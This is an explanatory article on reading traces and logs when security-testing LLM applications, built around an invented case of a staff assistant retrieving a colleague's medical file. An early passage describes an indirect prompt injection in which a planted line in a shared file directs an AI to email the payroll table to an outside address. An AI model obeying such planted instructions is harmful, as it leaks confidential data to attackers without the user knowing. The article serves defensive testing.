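# Application traces and logs as evidence in security assessments of AI systems

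## What a trace records and what a tester sees without it

A large language model (LLM) is a program, trained on very large amounts of text, that continues whatever text it receives. Companies usually give users access to the model through an application, which is ordinary software that assembles the text the model will read (the prompt), runs searches and functions for the model, and passes an answer back. A trace is the linked record of all the steps an application took to handle one request. Engineers developed tracing to find slow or failing services, but security testers also use traces for other purposes, such as learning which documents an application opened and under whose account.

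Testers need the trace because the answer on the screen is weak evidence about security. An application may read a confidential file and leave it out of the reply, or fetch the right figure through an account with far too many permissions. In both cases the user gets a good answer, and a tester who sees only that answer can't detect the problem.

### Applications that search and act

A model on its own can draw only on its training and the prompt. In a retrieval-augmented application, software first searches a collection of documents for the passages most similar to the question, then adds some or all of them to the prompt before the model answers. Each passage the search returns is called a retrieved chunk, whether or not it is added to the prompt. The search returns the same passages whoever is asking, unless a developer has added a filter on permissions.

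A tool call is a model's request to run a function with given arguments. The model writes the function's name and arguments as text, software runs the function, and the result goes into the next prompt. An agent is an application in which the model chooses its own sequence of tool calls to complete a task. OpenTelemetry is an open-source project that maintains shared formats and code for tracing. The examples in its *Semantic Conventions for GenAI agent and framework spans* include looking up a customer's purchase history, emailing a colleague and completing a financial transaction. Each of these actions needs someone's authority. The agent can act with authority given by a user, which is called delegated identity, or through a standing account that belongs to the application and is the same for every user.

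The Model Context Protocol (MCP) is a common format that applications use to reach tools and data from different suppliers. Model Context Protocol's *Architecture* (2026) describes the application as the host, which holds the conversation and enforces consent. Servers offer the tools and documents, and the host creates a separate client to connect to each server. A server should receive only the context it needs, and should not be able to read the whole conversation or see into other servers. This helps protect privacy, but it also means that the operator of one server cannot reconstruct a whole request from that server's records.

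Prompt injection is text that makes a model follow an attacker's instructions. It is indirect when the text arrives through documents or tool results, so the attacker never has to use the application. Suppose someone adds a line to a shared file that tells any AI reading it to email the payroll table to an outside address. Weeks later, an employee asks about pay dates, and the search returns that passage. The model receives the question and the planted line in one prompt and can't reliably tell instructions from quoted text. If it follows the planted line, it makes a tool call to send the email. The employee sees only its answer about pay dates, which may still be correct.

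### How an application produces a trace

A span is one timed step within a trace, such as a model call, a document search or a tool call. Instrumentation is the code that creates spans while the application runs. According to OpenTelemetry's *Traces*, a span holds a name, start and end times, a status, its own identifier, and the identifiers of its trace and its parent, the span that gave rise to it. It also holds attributes, which are named fields such as the tool's name or its arguments. The first span has no parent, so software that displays traces can start there and use the identifiers to rebuild the tree. Work that an application queues for later may be recorded in a second trace, with an optional link back to the first. For example, if an assistant schedules an email for the evening, the request could be in one trace and the sending in another.

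Developers can write instrumentation into their own code or attach it from outside without editing the program. OpenTelemetry's *Instrumentation* says the second method shows what happens at an application's edges. OpenTelemetry's *Zero-code* says attached instrumentation typically covers the libraries a program uses, so it picks up web requests, database calls and message queues, but typically misses the application's own code. A rule such as "only managers may open this folder" is often in that code. A trace can therefore show a tester the database query but not the permission check that ran just before it.

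A request usually passes through several services, which must link their spans into one trace. When one service calls another, it sends the trace's identifier and the identifier of its own current span. The receiving service creates a new span in the same trace and sets the caller's span as its parent. OpenTelemetry's *Context propagation* describes the web request header that usually carries these identifiers. The header contains a version number, the trace identifier, the parent span's identifier and a set of flags.

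MCP servers can also run as local processes, where no web headers exist to carry the identifiers. The release candidate for the protocol's July 2026 version therefore documented a place for them in a metadata field inside the call, under the same names that web requests use (Model Context Protocol, 2026). Several code libraries already did this. According to the accepted proposal behind the change, from Model Context Protocol, the names had to be fixed because a library that used its own would break the trace. Where everyone follows the convention, one tree can run from the host through a tool call to the server and on to whatever the server calls next. The final version, published on July 28, 2026 (Model Context Protocol, 2026), also dropped the session identifier that earlier calls could carry. An assessor who used to group a server's records by session now needs the trace identifier or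 some handle that the application supplies.

Finished spans go to a trace store, the database or hosted platform where people keep and read traces. They can go there directly, but for anything beyond a small or trial installation, OpenTelemetry's *Collector* recommends sending them first to a collector, a separate program that receives, processes and forwards the data. The collector can batch spans, retry failed deliveries, encrypt data and filter out anything sensitive. A tool's arguments can therefore be missing from a trace because the instrumentation never captured them or because the collector removed them.

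Content capture means recording the text of prompts, answers, tool arguments and results, not just metadata about them. OpenTelemetry's conventions for agents, which are still in development, make recording the chat history and the system's standing instructions to the model opt-in. A trace without them can show that a model call took place, how long it took and how much text went in, but not what the model read.

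### Traces, ordinary logs and audit logs

Nearly every program writes logs. OpenTelemetry's *Logs* defines a log as a timestamped text record, with or without a fixed structure. An OpenTelemetry post on logging gives two differences between spans and logs. A span has a duration and an explicit place in a hierarchy, whereas a single logged event doesn't show how it relates to the others. For example, if a hundred people are using an assistant at once, a log line may show that the application opened a medical file at 10:02:11, but not which person's question caused it. However, logging software can add the trace identifier to each line, which lets a tester group the lines by request.

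An audit log is a record kept for accountability, usually with a fixed set of events chosen by the vendor. The *audit log* entry in the US National Institute of Standards and Technology's glossary includes the definition "documentary evidence of specific events". *Audit Logging*, from the European cloud software project ApeiroRA, lists failed logins, permission changes, access to sensitive information and changes to data as typical events. Unlike with everyday application logs, providers usually have to keep audit logs for a long time and must guarantee that every event arrives. ApeiroRA aims to bring this kind of audit logging to OpenTelemetry, but the plan is still under development, and ordinary traces do not carry that guarantee today.

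Audit logs and traces complement each other in an investigation. An audit log that records a file access may be guaranteed complete, but it will usually lack the search query, model call and tool result that led to the access. A trace includes those steps but has no guarantee of completeness. NIST's definition of an *audit trail* sets a higher standard, a chronological record sufficient to reconstruct the events that led to an operation, from inception to result. Meeting that standard for an LLM application will often require both records, joined by an identifier or at least by time.

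### What each kind of testing can see

In endpoint-level testing, a tester sends inputs to an application and sees only its responses. This method is worth keeping because it needs little help from the developers and shows what an outside attacker would see. However, the tester cannot distinguish a safe application from one that did something improper and then gave a harmless reply.

Grey-box testers also read some internal information, in this case traces, without full knowledge of the system. NIST's entry for *focused testing*, the formal name for grey-box testing, assumes "some knowledge" of internal structure and implementation. Its entry for *comprehensive testing*, or white-box testing, assumes explicit and substantial knowledge, which in practice means source code and configuration. Traces are still useful to testers who have the source code. They can read the code to confirm that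 a permission check exists, but they need the trace to see whether it ran for a particular user's question, and the trace shows this only if someone instrumented the check.

### An invented example: Ana and the staff assistant

The following case is invented. Ana works in the accounts department of a company that has an assistant for questions about employment. She asks how much parental leave she can take. This is what the endpoint returns:

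```
status:  200 OK
time:    2.9 seconds
answer:  You can take 16 weeks of parental leave at full pay.
         You have not used any of it yet.
source:  Staff handbook, "Parental leave"
```

The answer cites a proper source and mentions nobody other than Ana. An endpoint-level tester who checks it against the handbook and Ana's leave record finds it correct on both counts and marks the case as passed.

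The trace of the same request, with content capture switched off, looks like this:

```
answer question                     0.00-2.90 s   user: ana
|
+-- model call: write search query  0.05-0.55 s
|
+-- document search                 0.56-0.81 s   chunks returned: 5
|     1  Staff handbook, "Parental leave"
|     2  Staff handbook, "Pay during leave"
|     3  Occupational health file, Tomas Berg
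|     4  Leave request form
|     5  Staff handbook, "Returning to work"
|
+-- model call: choose tool         0.83-1.40 s
|
+-- tool call: leave lookup         1.42-1.70 s   account: hr-assistant
|
+-- model call: write answer        1.72-2.88 s
```

The third retrieved chunk comes from the medical file of a colleague, Tomas Berg. He presumably had a period of leave, and the wording of his file resembled Ana's question. The trace shows that the search step returned this passage for Ana's request. It does not show that the model read the passage, because the prompt's text is missing and the application may have passed on only the best two chunks. The trace alone also does not prove that anyone broke a rule. An occupational health nurse might be allowed to open that file, so the tester has to look up who has access. If accounts staff do not, the fault is real even though nothing leaked this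 time, and the obvious next test is a question from Ana's account worded more like the medical file.

The leave lookup returned the right result, but it ran under hr-assistant, a shared service account that the application uses for all employees. The personnel system therefore received the request from hr-assistant, which can presumably read everyone's leave. This trace does not show whether any check would stop Ana from getting Tomas's balance by asking for it. A tester can find out by making that request from Ana's account and reading the new trace.

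The tree also has no authorization decision, meaning a recorded allow or deny for a particular identity, action and resource. The tester can report that the trace contains no decision, but not that the assistant checks nothing, because the application may check in code that isn't instrumented, or the personnel system may check and write the outcome to its own log. The spans' status doesn't help either, because OpenTelemetry's default status means that an operation finished without an error, which is also true of a search that successfully returns a forbidden file.

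### Questions to ask of a trace

A span is decent evidence that a step happened, but a missing span is evidence that it didn't happen only if the instrumentation reliably records that step. Testers can check this easily by using a test account to request a file that the account is definitely not allowed to open, then looking for the refusal in the trace. If the refusal leaves no span, they can conclude very little from the lack of an authorization decision in Ana's trace.

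Developers often keep only a sample of traces to save money, so there may be no record of the request that matters. Traces can also have gaps where one service stops passing identifiers to the next, sometimes for good security reasons. OpenTelemetry advises caution with identifiers from untrusted callers and suggests that services may want to ignore them, or to withhold their own from outside services. If a team follows this advice, its traces stop at the company's border. Kovrr's *OTel Report 2026* (2026), an analysis by a vendor with an interest in the matter, links the weakness to the design goals of Dapper, Google's early tracing system, which were low overhead, transparency to applications and scalability, but not completeness or integrity. That account is fair, and it suggests testing completeness in each installation.

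The tester should also ask what produced the record. It was usually the application under test, and a faulty or compromised application can write faulty spans. Instrumentation that works correctly can still record a wrong value. Under OpenTelemetry's conventions, the field for the model's provider is filled in from the instrumentation's best knowledge and may not name the company that actually ran the model. Spans from an outside MCP server depend on that server's operator, and OpenTelemetry warns that attackers can send forged trace headers to manipulate tracing data. A second record from a separate component is therefore a valuable check. In Ana's case, the personnel system's own log could confirm that the lookup took place, and when.

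Last, a trace may not show whose authority the application used. The US government's standard control on audit records, as reproduced in Tarleton State University's *AU-3*, requires the type of event, its time, place, source and outcome, and the identity of any people or objects involved. A span has built-in fields for a name, times and a status, but it records identity only if a developer adds it as an attribute. Ana's trace has two identities, ana on the first span and hr-assistant on the lookup, but it doesn't record that hr-assistant was acting for Ana or that her rights limited what it could fetch. If she had asked for Tomas's leave instead, and the assistant had fetched it, the tree could have looked the same.

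## OpenTelemetry's fields for generative AI, read by a security tester

Ana's trace listed the titles of five retrieved chunks and the account that looked up her leave because someone had chosen to record those details. If the application had followed OpenTelemetry's conventions for generative AI with the default settings, the trace would have shown that a document search took place but not what it returned, and the tester would not have learned about Tomas Berg's medical file.

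Semantic conventions are agreed names for spans and attributes, which let people read traces from different companies' software the same way. The conventions for generative AI cover model calls, agent invocations, document searches, tool executions and MCP calls. Before a test starts, a security tester can use them as a list of evidence to ask for.

### What instrumentation must record and what it can leave out

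OpenTelemetry's *Semantic conventions for generative client AI spans* gives each attribute a requirement level. Instrumentation must record required attributes. It must record conditionally required attributes when a stated condition holds; for example, it must record the error type after an error. It should record recommended attributes by default if it can, and it records opt-in attributes only if someone turns them on. The table below follows the April 2026 text, OpenTelemetry's version 1.40.0, and leaves out minor settings.

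| Span | Required | Conditionally required | Recommended | Opt-in |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Model call | Operation, provider | Requested model, conversation identifier, error type | Model that answered, response identifier, reason for stopping, token counts, server address | System instructions, input messages, output messages, tool definitions |
| Agent invocation | Operation, provider | Agent name, identifier and version; conversation and data source identifiers; requested model; error type | Model that answered, token counts, server address | Message content |
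| Retrieval | Operation | Data source identifier, provider, requested model, error type | Server address | Query text, retrieved documents |
| Tool execution | Operation | Error type | Tool name, type and description; call identifier | Arguments, result |

An application can meet every requirement in this table without giving a tester the model's input, the documents a search returned or the arguments a tool received. Field names and requirement levels can also change while the conventions are in development.

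### Model calls

The span for a model call has some value even with content capture off. It should record the model that the application requested and the model that answered. If a company tested and approved one model, a difference between the two names suggests that some requests went to another. The server address helps a tester check whether staff data went to an unapproved supplier. If the request passed through a proxy, the span should give the address of the server behind it, but instrumentation can't always find that address.

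Token counts can show that an application didn't pass all the retrieved text to the model. Tokens are the word fragments in which models read and write text. Suppose the five chunks from Ana's search come to 2,500 tokens, and the model call that produced her answer took in 900. The application can't have passed on all five chunks in full, although the count doesn't show what it left out. The input count should include tokens the provider had cached from earlier requests, but OpenTelemetry asks only for a best effort, so a tester should allow for some error.

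The input messages are the best evidence for prompt injection. They hold the chat history the application gave the model, and the instrumentation must keep them in the order the application sent them. In the payroll attack described earlier, they would show whether the planted line from the shared file reached the model. But instrumentation may shorten or filter the messages, and trace stores often limit the size of an attribute. If the planted line is missing, the tester should first check for truncation.

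Each message also has a role, such as user, assistant or tool. Text with the role "tool" came back from a tool call, which helps a tester trace an indirect injection to its source. But the role doesn't reliably show who wrote the text. Many applications paste retrieved chunks into the same message as the user's question, so any injected instructions in those chunks also have the role "user".

A tester can read the system instructions to see whether the developer relied on the model to enforce a rule. An instruction such as "never reveal another employee's records" is much weaker protection than a permission check in code. The system instructions attribute holds only instructions that the application sent separately from the chat history. Instructions sent in the history appear among the input messages, so the model may have had instructions even if the attribute is empty.

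Output messages record what the model returned, including any tool calls it requested and their arguments. They don't prove what the user saw, because the application may have filtered or rewritten the answer. They also don't prove that a requested tool ran.

Tool definitions list the functions the model could have requested, so they can reveal a problem that no single run would show, such as an assistant for employment questions that also has a tool for sending email outside the company. The April 2026 text recommends against recording the definitions by default because they can be very large. OpenTelemetry's *Gen AI*, the later registry of attribute names, recommends leaving out only the optional parts of each definition. A tester who suspects that an attacker has hidden instructions in a tool's description should check whether the description was left out.

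Attacks can also take several turns. A user might give an assistant a harmless-looking instruction in one message and exploit it three messages later, and each message may have its own trace. The conversation identifier links these traces. Instrumentation should record it when it is readily available, for example when the framework manages the chat history. For developers who manage the history in their own code, adding the identifier is optional, and without it the tester has to match traces by time and user.

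Retrieval applications also call embedding models, which turn text into lists of numbers so that software can compare passages by meaning. The span for such a call has attributes for the provider, the model and the number of input tokens, but none for the text, not even an opt-in one. A company that indexes its files with an outside embedding service sends that service the files' contents. The trace can show that the company made these calls and roughly how much text they carried, but the tester needs the indexing program's records to learn which files were sent.

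### Agent invocations

An agent invocation span typically encloses the model and tool calls that the agent makes. It records the agent's name, ID and version where available. When retesting, a tester can use the version to confirm that a fault and its supposed fix came from different releases.

OpenTelemetry distinguishes agents that run inside the application's own process from remote agent services. A remote agent runs on the supplier's machines, so the calling application can record that it invoked the agent and what came back. The agent's searches and tool calls appear in the trace only if the supplier produces spans for them and shares them.

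None of the generative AI attributes in OpenTelemetry's registry identifies the user, and an agent's identifier shows only which software acted. A tester needs a recorded authorization decision to find out whether the user's permissions limited the request. A separate Kubernetes proposal covers such records.

### Retrieval

OpenTelemetry requires only one attribute on every retrieval span, the operation's name, which shows that a search took place. The data source identifier should indicate which collection the application searched. OpenTelemetry recommends using the AI system's name for the collection rather than the underlying database's or file store's. A tester who finds "H7STPQYOND", one of the conventions' examples, in this attribute has to ask the developers which collection it refers to before looking up who may read that collection.

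The query text and the list of retrieved documents are both opt-in. The query is useful because the model often rewrites the user's question before the search. If Ana's question about parental leave became a query about "employee leave, medical grounds", that rewrite could explain why the search found Tomas's file.

For each retrieved document the conventions ask for at least an identifier and a relevance score. The following span is invented, but it uses the standard names:

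```
gen_ai.operation.name        retrieval
gen_ai.data_source.id        hr-documents
gen_ai.retrieval.query.text  parental leave entitlement
gen_ai.retrieval.documents   id: doc_118   score: 0.91
                             id: doc_204   score: 0.88
                             id: doc_733   score: 0.84
```

The span doesn't record whether doc_733 is Tomas's file, so the tester must look up the identifier in the document store. Someone may have replaced the document or changed its permissions since the span was recorded. The identifier may also refer to a whole file when the search returned only one paragraph of it.

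The retrieval table has no attribute for the user's permissions or the document's access label, such as "occupational health only". The words "at least" allow developers to add a label to each document, but another company's tools won't look for it. A standard retrieval span therefore can't show by itself that a search broke an access rule.

Which documents a span lists also depends on where the instrumentation is placed. Some applications search first and remove forbidden documents afterwards. A span that covers only the search will still list the forbidden documents, and a tester could report a leak that never happened. Comparing the list with the input messages is a good way to rule this out.

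### Tool and MCP calls

A tool execution span should name the tool and, where available, record its type, its description and the call's identifier. Recording the arguments and result is opt-in. An arguments attribute for the leave lookup might contain an employee number, from which the tester could see whether the assistant asked for Ana's balance or Tomas's. The attribute wouldn't show how the personnel system used that number or which account it checked.

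The call identifier connects the model's request to the tool's execution. If the output messages contain a request whose identifier doesn't match any tool span, software may have blocked the call, a person may have declined it, or the instrumentation may not cover that tool. With content capture off, the model's request isn't in the trace, so the tester can't make this comparison.

The last of these explanations is often the most likely for a company's own tools, because attached instrumentation typically misses application code. OpenTelemetry encourages developers to add spans for such tools by hand. If they don't, a function that reads payroll data may be missing from the trace even though a generic web search appears in full. A tester can find such gaps by triggering each tool once from a test account and counting the spans.

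The conventions define a tool call's result as what the tool returned if it ran successfully, so when a personnel system refuses a request, the span may have an error type but not the text of the refusal. A tool can also return "access denied" as an ordinary result, which makes the span look like a success. Testers therefore should not count refusals by error status alone.

OpenTelemetry's *MCP* lists separate attributes for MCP calls, including the method name, protocol version and resource address. One example address points to the structure of a customer database. A tester can check an address like this against a list of permissions far more easily than an arbitrary document identifier. But the address shows only what the client requested, so the tester still needs the server's response to know whether the client received it.

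The conventions define spans for both the client and the server in an MCP call. Where different teams run the two sides and both record spans, the tester can compare two records of the same call. MCP instrumentation may also record a tool call that the application would otherwise record as a tool-execution span. Searching a trace store for only one of these span types can miss calls, and adding both types together can count the same call twice.

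### Where the text goes when a team records it

OpenTelemetry describes three ways to handle instructions, inputs and outputs. By default, instrumentation records none of them, because the text is often sensitive and large. A team can record them on the spans, which suits test environments with made-up data. For production, where volume or privacy is a concern, OpenTelemetry recommends keeping the text in a separate store and putting a reference to it on the span. The store can then have its own access controls.

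Testers should ask about that store even if the spans look empty. Under the conventions, the code that uploads the text should work independently of the settings for recording it on spans, and should run whether or not the system keeps the trace. The store can therefore hold the full prompt for a request even if the system discarded the trace to save money. The conventions don't yet specify a common way to write the references, so testers may need the developers' help to follow one from a span to its text.

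The upload code can also change the messages before the instrumentation puts them on the span, for example to remove names or bank details. The record is then safer to read but no longer matches what the model received, so a tester who wants to repeat an attack exactly will need the original messages.

*OpenTelemetry GenAI Conventions* (Wang, 2026) describes an opt-in event that can carry the chat history and model settings separately from the trace, though not every programming language supports it yet. A tester who reads only spans could wrongly conclude that a team captured no content when the text is in the event records.

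### Versions, and the move to a new repository

OpenTelemetry formed a working group on generative AI in April 2024, at first to trace calls from applications to models, according to Greptime (2026), a database vendor. Version 1.37 of OpenTelemetry's conventions revised the message attributes, version 1.39 added MCP, and version 1.40 added retrieval. An application with older instrumentation may therefore have no standard retrieval spans, even if it searches documents for every question.

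The message revision can also mislead testers. Instrumentation used to record the chat history as a separate event for each message, an approach that OpenTelemetry's changelog lists as replaced. Instrumentation written for version 1.36 or earlier should keep producing the old format unless someone sets an environment variable to request the new one. A search for `gen_ai.input.messages` can therefore come back empty even when the prompts are in the trace store under an older name, such as `gen_ai.prompt`, so testers should search for both old and new names.

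In 2026 the project moved the generative AI conventions out of its main collection. Ecosyste.ms' *OpenTelemetry GenAI Semantic Conventions*, a third-party index, says the new repository was created on May 5. Wang writes that the definitions moved in June, with version 1.42.0 of the main conventions, so that they could develop on their own schedule. The main registry now marks the current attributes as moved, and OpenTelemetry's *Moved* says the project no longer maintains the old page there. The attributes are still in use, and a "deprecated" label in the old collection may only mean that the definition has moved.

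According to Wang, the new repository had no official release as of August 21, 2026, and its conventions were still in development. An assessor should check its release list on the day of a test and record which version of the conventions the application's instrumentation follows. Without the version, a later reader can't tell whether a missing attribute was switched off, had another name or did not yet exist.

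Software can do part of this checking. OpenTelemetry's *Building an Agent Harness for OTel Instrumentation with GenAI Semantic Conventions* (2026) describes a trial in which AI agents inspect a framework, plan its instrumentation and write the code. A program called Weaver then checks the resulting spans against the conventions, and engineers review the plan and the code. Weaver could also help a tester find misnamed or missing attributes.

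### Guardrail spans and threat-detection attributes

A guardrail checks the text going into or out of a model or tool and can allow, change or block it. The attributes described so far don't record what a guardrail decided, so if an assistant refuses a malicious request, the tester can't tell whether a guardrail blocked it or the model declined, which it might not do next time.

Semantic-conventions pull request 3233, a proposed change to the conventions, would add a span called `apply_guardrail`. It opened on December 22, 2025, and was still an unmerged draft in May 2026. Neither the main registry nor Wang's August list of operations from the new repository includes it. Wang's list does include planning and memory operations that the registry lacks, so the new repository has already moved ahead of the registry. Testers should treat the guardrail span as a proposal unless the new repository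 shows that the maintainers have adopted it.

Specification pull request 5098 is a separate proposal for threat-detection attributes. The registry's generative AI list does not include them, so a tester should not expect to find them in an ordinary trace.

Microsoft has already built guardrail spans into its OpenTelemetry libraries. These spans can record the guardrail's name, what it checked, its decision and an optional reason. Each span should sit directly beneath the model or tool call that the guardrail protects, so a tester can see which step the check covered. If several guardrails ran in turn, each can have its own span.

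A guardrail span can also hold findings. Microsoft's *Interface GuardrailFinding* requires each finding to have a risk category and a severity, and allows a score from 0 to 1 and the name and version of the policy that triggered it. Findings may include metadata, such as "field:bcc" or "pattern:ssn", which must not contain personal information. A tester could learn from "field:bcc" that a guardrail flagged a hidden email recipient, without seeing the recipient's address.

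Microsoft's sample code creates the span with the decision "allow", runs the check, and changes the decision to "deny" if it finds hate speech. If the check crashed before finishing, the span might still show "allow". The sample is only an illustration, and an application can be written differently. A tester can find out how an application behaves by making the guardrail fail on purpose and reading the span.

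Other products use other names, so a search for blocked requests across several products needs a separate query for each. NVIDIA's NeMo Guardrails, a library for adding such checks, sets an attribute called `rail.stop` to true when a check blocks a request, according to NVIDIA's documentation. NVIDIA's *Span Reference* explains that the library's default engine keeps a log while it handles a request and reconstructs the spans from it afterwards. If the program crashes halfway through, the spans for that request may never appear. None of these guardrail decisions shows whether the user had permission to read a document.

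### OpenInference and the tools that display traces

OpenInference is another set of conventions for AI applications, built on OpenTelemetry and maintained by Arize. It labels each span with a kind, such as model, retriever, tool, agent or guardrail. It also has a kind for rerankers, which reorder retrieved chunks and often discard some, so a tester can see which chunks the reranker kept.

For a security tester, OpenInference differs from OpenTelemetry mainly in what it can record about retrieval. An OpenInference document can include the chunk's text and free-form metadata as well as an identifier and score. The metadata can contain a document's access label if the search index stores the label and the search returns it, but OpenInference doesn't define a dedicated permissions attribute. It does define an attribute for the user's identifier. OpenInference instrumentation generally records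 content unless someone hides it, while OpenTelemetry leaves content out by default.

Several products collect and display these records. LangSmith, from the company behind the LangChain framework, takes traces from its own library or from OpenTelemetry and shows each request as a tree of steps with inputs and outputs. Langfuse is an open-source platform that companies can run themselves, and it can group traces by user and session if the application supplies those identifiers. Phoenix, Arize's open-source tool, receives OpenInference spans and can show each retrieved chunk with its score. MLflow began as a tool for tracking machine-learning experiments. It now also records traces and can automatically instrument many common AI libraries.

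Wang points out that trace stores vary in how they index, display and retain data, so the same trace can look different in each one. A tester should export the raw spans before reporting that an attribute is missing, because the store may have kept it without displaying it.

### Which attribute answers which question

The table below uses OpenTelemetry's names except in the row on guardrails.

| Security question | Attribute to read | Remaining gap |
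|---|---|---|
| What text did the model receive? | `gen_ai.input.messages`, `gen_ai.system_instructions` | Opt-in; software may shorten or alter the text before recording it |
| Which documents did the search return? | `gen_ai.retrieval.documents` | Opt-in; may hold only identifiers and scores |
| Did the user have permission to read them? | None | The tester must compare the identifiers with the document store's permissions at the time |
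| Which collection did the application search? | `gen_ai.data_source.id` | The name may differ from the one in the underlying store |
| Which tools could the model request? | `gen_ai.tool.definitions` | Opt-in; descriptions may be missing |
| Did a requested tool run? | `gen_ai.output.messages`, matched by `gen_ai.tool.call.id` | A missing span can mean a blocked call or missing instrumentation |
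| What did the tool receive and return? | `gen_ai.tool.call.arguments`, `gen_ai.tool.call.result` | Opt-in; a failed call may leave no result, and neither attribute shows the effect on other systems |
| Which resource did an MCP client request? | `mcp.resource.uri` | Does not show whether the server allowed access |
| Whose authority did the agent use? | None; `gen_ai.agent.id` identifies only the agent | No standard generative AI attribute for the user or for delegated identity |
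| Do several requests belong to one conversation? | `gen_ai.conversation.id` | Often missing when the application manages its own chat history |
| Where did the prompt go? | `server.address`, `gen_ai.response.model` | A proxy can hide the final destination |
| Did a guardrail block the request? | Product-specific, such as NVIDIA's `rail.stop` | The common guardrail span is a draft |

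## Retrieval traces that show documents a user should not reach

In early 2026 Microsoft 365 Copilot Chat, an assistant that answers questions from a company's emails and documents, summarised emails labelled "confidential" even though companies had set a data loss prevention (DLP) policy to keep Copilot away from anything with that label. According to Office365ITPros' *Code Error Allowed Copilot Chat to Expose Confidential Information* (2026), customers first reported the fault on January 21. In its February 3 advisory, Microsoft attributed the fault to a "code issue" that let Copilot pick up labelled items in the Sent Items and Drafts folders, and it was rolling out a fix by February 10. Microsoft had not disclosed how many organisations were affected when Knutsson reported on the fault in *Why the Microsoft 365 Copilot bug matters for data security*.

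ITPro's *Microsoft Copilot bug saw AI snoop on confidential emails* quotes a Microsoft statement that the users had written the emails and that nobody gained access to information they weren't already authorized to see. TechRadar's *Microsoft admits an Office bug exposed confidential user emails to Copilot* points out that Copilot presumably reached whole threads, including other people's messages. Those messages were still in the user's own mailbox. The software did not enforce a rule about what the assistant may process, which is a different failure from showing one employee the contents of another's mailbox.

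Microsoft has not published traces of the fault, but a retrieval trace could probably have shown it. If the search span listed the documents it returned, a tester could have looked up each email's label and folder and seen that labelled emails were coming from only two folders. If the exclusion check had its own span, the tester could also have seen whether the check failed to run or ran and gave the wrong result. The tester would have had to compare the emails with the exclusion policy, because users may read their own mail and a comparison with mailbox permissions would have found nothing. Microsoft was better placed to do this than its customers, who have Copilot's audit log but not its internal spans.

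The Office365ITPros article describes sending a confidential email about an invented "Project Bunny" after the fix and then asking Copilot about it. Copilot replied that it had found an internal reference but could not disclose the content. The search evidently still found the email, and the policy took effect between the search and the answer.

### Retrieved, in the prompt, used, cited

A search can return a chunk that never enters the prompt. A chunk can enter the prompt without influencing the answer, and it can influence the answer without being listed as a source. A tester therefore needs different evidence to show that a chunk was retrieved, entered the prompt, influenced the answer or was listed as a source.

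The document list on a retrieval span shows what the search returned, and the input messages show what entered the prompt, if both opt-in fields are switched on. No field records whether a retrieved chunk influenced the answer. To test this, a tester can put an invented fact in a document and look for it in the answer, or run the request again without the chunk and compare the answers, preferably several times because a model's wording varies. Even if the invented fact is missing, the chunk may still have affected the answer. For example, an assistant that has read Tomas's medical file might advise Ana to speak to him "when he is back" without mentioning his illness.

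Citations are poor evidence of what the model used. Some applications list every chunk in the prompt as a source, and others let the model write its own citations, which can be wrong or incomplete. But a citation can itself leak information. *Stop Copilot Summarizing Confidential Files with Purview DLP* (Bertram, 2026) lists citations and titles among the things that still leak after a company blocks Copilot from processing labelled files. Ana could learn about planned redundancies from a title such as "Redundancy plan, accounts department".

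Researchers also count different events, sometimes under the same name. *Securing the Agent* (Arceo and Narsing, 2026) defines "cross-tenant leakage rate" as the share of probes for which the search returns at least one forbidden chunk, where a tenant is a customer or department that shares a system with others. *Burn-After-Use for Preventing Data Leakage through a Secure Multi-Tenant Architecture* (2026) uses the same name for how often a system discloses information across tenants. An application that retrieves forbidden text for every probe but never repeats it in an answer would score 100% under the first definition and zero under the second.

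*LeakDojo* (2026), a study of attacks that extract documents from retrieval systems, separately counts the chunks an attacker gets the system to retrieve and the chunks that leak. It treats a query as a successful leak if the answer contains more than half of a retrieved chunk's words in their original order, with gaps allowed. That test misses most paraphrases, which can also expose protected facts. Liu, Wang and colleagues (2026), in *Protection Is Not One Event*, tested a filter that removed copied phrases from answers. The filter cut verbatim copying of 20-token passages to zero, but an attacker who could ask three questions, adapting each to the last reply, still recovered 48.3% of the hidden facts from one model. The same researchers surveyed 118 papers on protecting retrieval systems and found that only 21 mainly measured whether protected content reached a user or could be reconstructed.

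### Three filtering designs and their traces

An application can check permissions before the search or after it. It can also skip the check and instruct the model to keep certain things secret. These invented traces show one question from Ana under each design:

```
FILTER BEFORE SEARCH
  document search     user: ana    filter: readable by accounts
                      returned: handbook-12, handbook-14, form-3
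  model call          input: handbook-12, handbook-14, form-3

FILTER AFTER SEARCH
  document search     returned: handbook-12, health-733, handbook-14
  permission check    user: ana    health-733: deny
  model call          input: handbook-12, handbook-14

INSTRUCTION TO THE MODEL
  document search     returned: handbook-12, health-733, handbook-14
  model call          instructions: "Never reveal health records."
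                      input: handbook-12, health-733, handbook-14
```

If the system filters documents before searching, it searches only those Ana may read, so no forbidden document should appear anywhere in the trace. Unless developers also recorded the filter in a custom attribute, the absence of forbidden documents is weak evidence that the filter worked, because there may have been none that matched the question.

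When filtering happens after the search, the search ranks all documents and a permission check then removes those Ana may not read. OpenFGA's *RAG Authorization*, part of a permissions system's documentation, describes two ways to do this. The application can check each candidate document in turn, or fetch the list of all documents the user may read and keep only the candidates on it. In either case, a forbidden document in the search span is normal, and the permission check's span shows whether the application removed it.

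When only an instruction to the model controls access, the prompt contains both the health file and a rule against repeating it. The trace contains no authorization decision because no software made one. *Privacy Conductor* (2026) argues that an LLM can't be trusted to decide who should receive a document, and *Beyond Document Retrieval* (2026) says that permission checks belong outside the model. Using AI to filter documents by role has not done especially well either. Liu and colleagues cite a test on 389 queries in which one such filter, ARBITER, had an F1 score of 0.89, while a simple fixed filter scored 0.93 to 0.94. F1 penalises both missed and mistaken blocks and has a maximum of 1.

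### What experiments have found

Arceo and Narsing, who work at Red Hat, tested a filter in OGX, the open-source framework in which they built their design. They created artificial finance, engineering and legal tenants with 100 documents each, and sent 300 probes in which a user from one tenant asked for another's documents. The filter reduced the share of probes that returned a forbidden chunk from 98–100% to zero. They also sent 90 prompt injection probes, and the filter reduced that share from 62–80% to zero. The filter and login check added about 19 milliseconds to a search, while a model usually takes seconds to answer.

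The filtering result is convincing because a check outside the model works the same way regardless of the prompt. The leak rate without a filter is less informative about everyday use because the probes deliberately asked for forbidden documents. In a separate benchmark with artificial embeddings, 52% of unfiltered queries leaked.

Filtering after search can also make an application much less useful. Arceo and Narsing measured how often the relevant passages appeared in the final five results after filtering. The score fell from 1.000 with 100 chunks in the collection to 0.100 with 1,000 and 0.002 with 50,000, even though the search fetched five times as many candidates as it needed. Other tenants' documents had taken nearly all the places before the filter ran. In a trace, this looks like a full list of candidates followed by an empty or nearly empty one.

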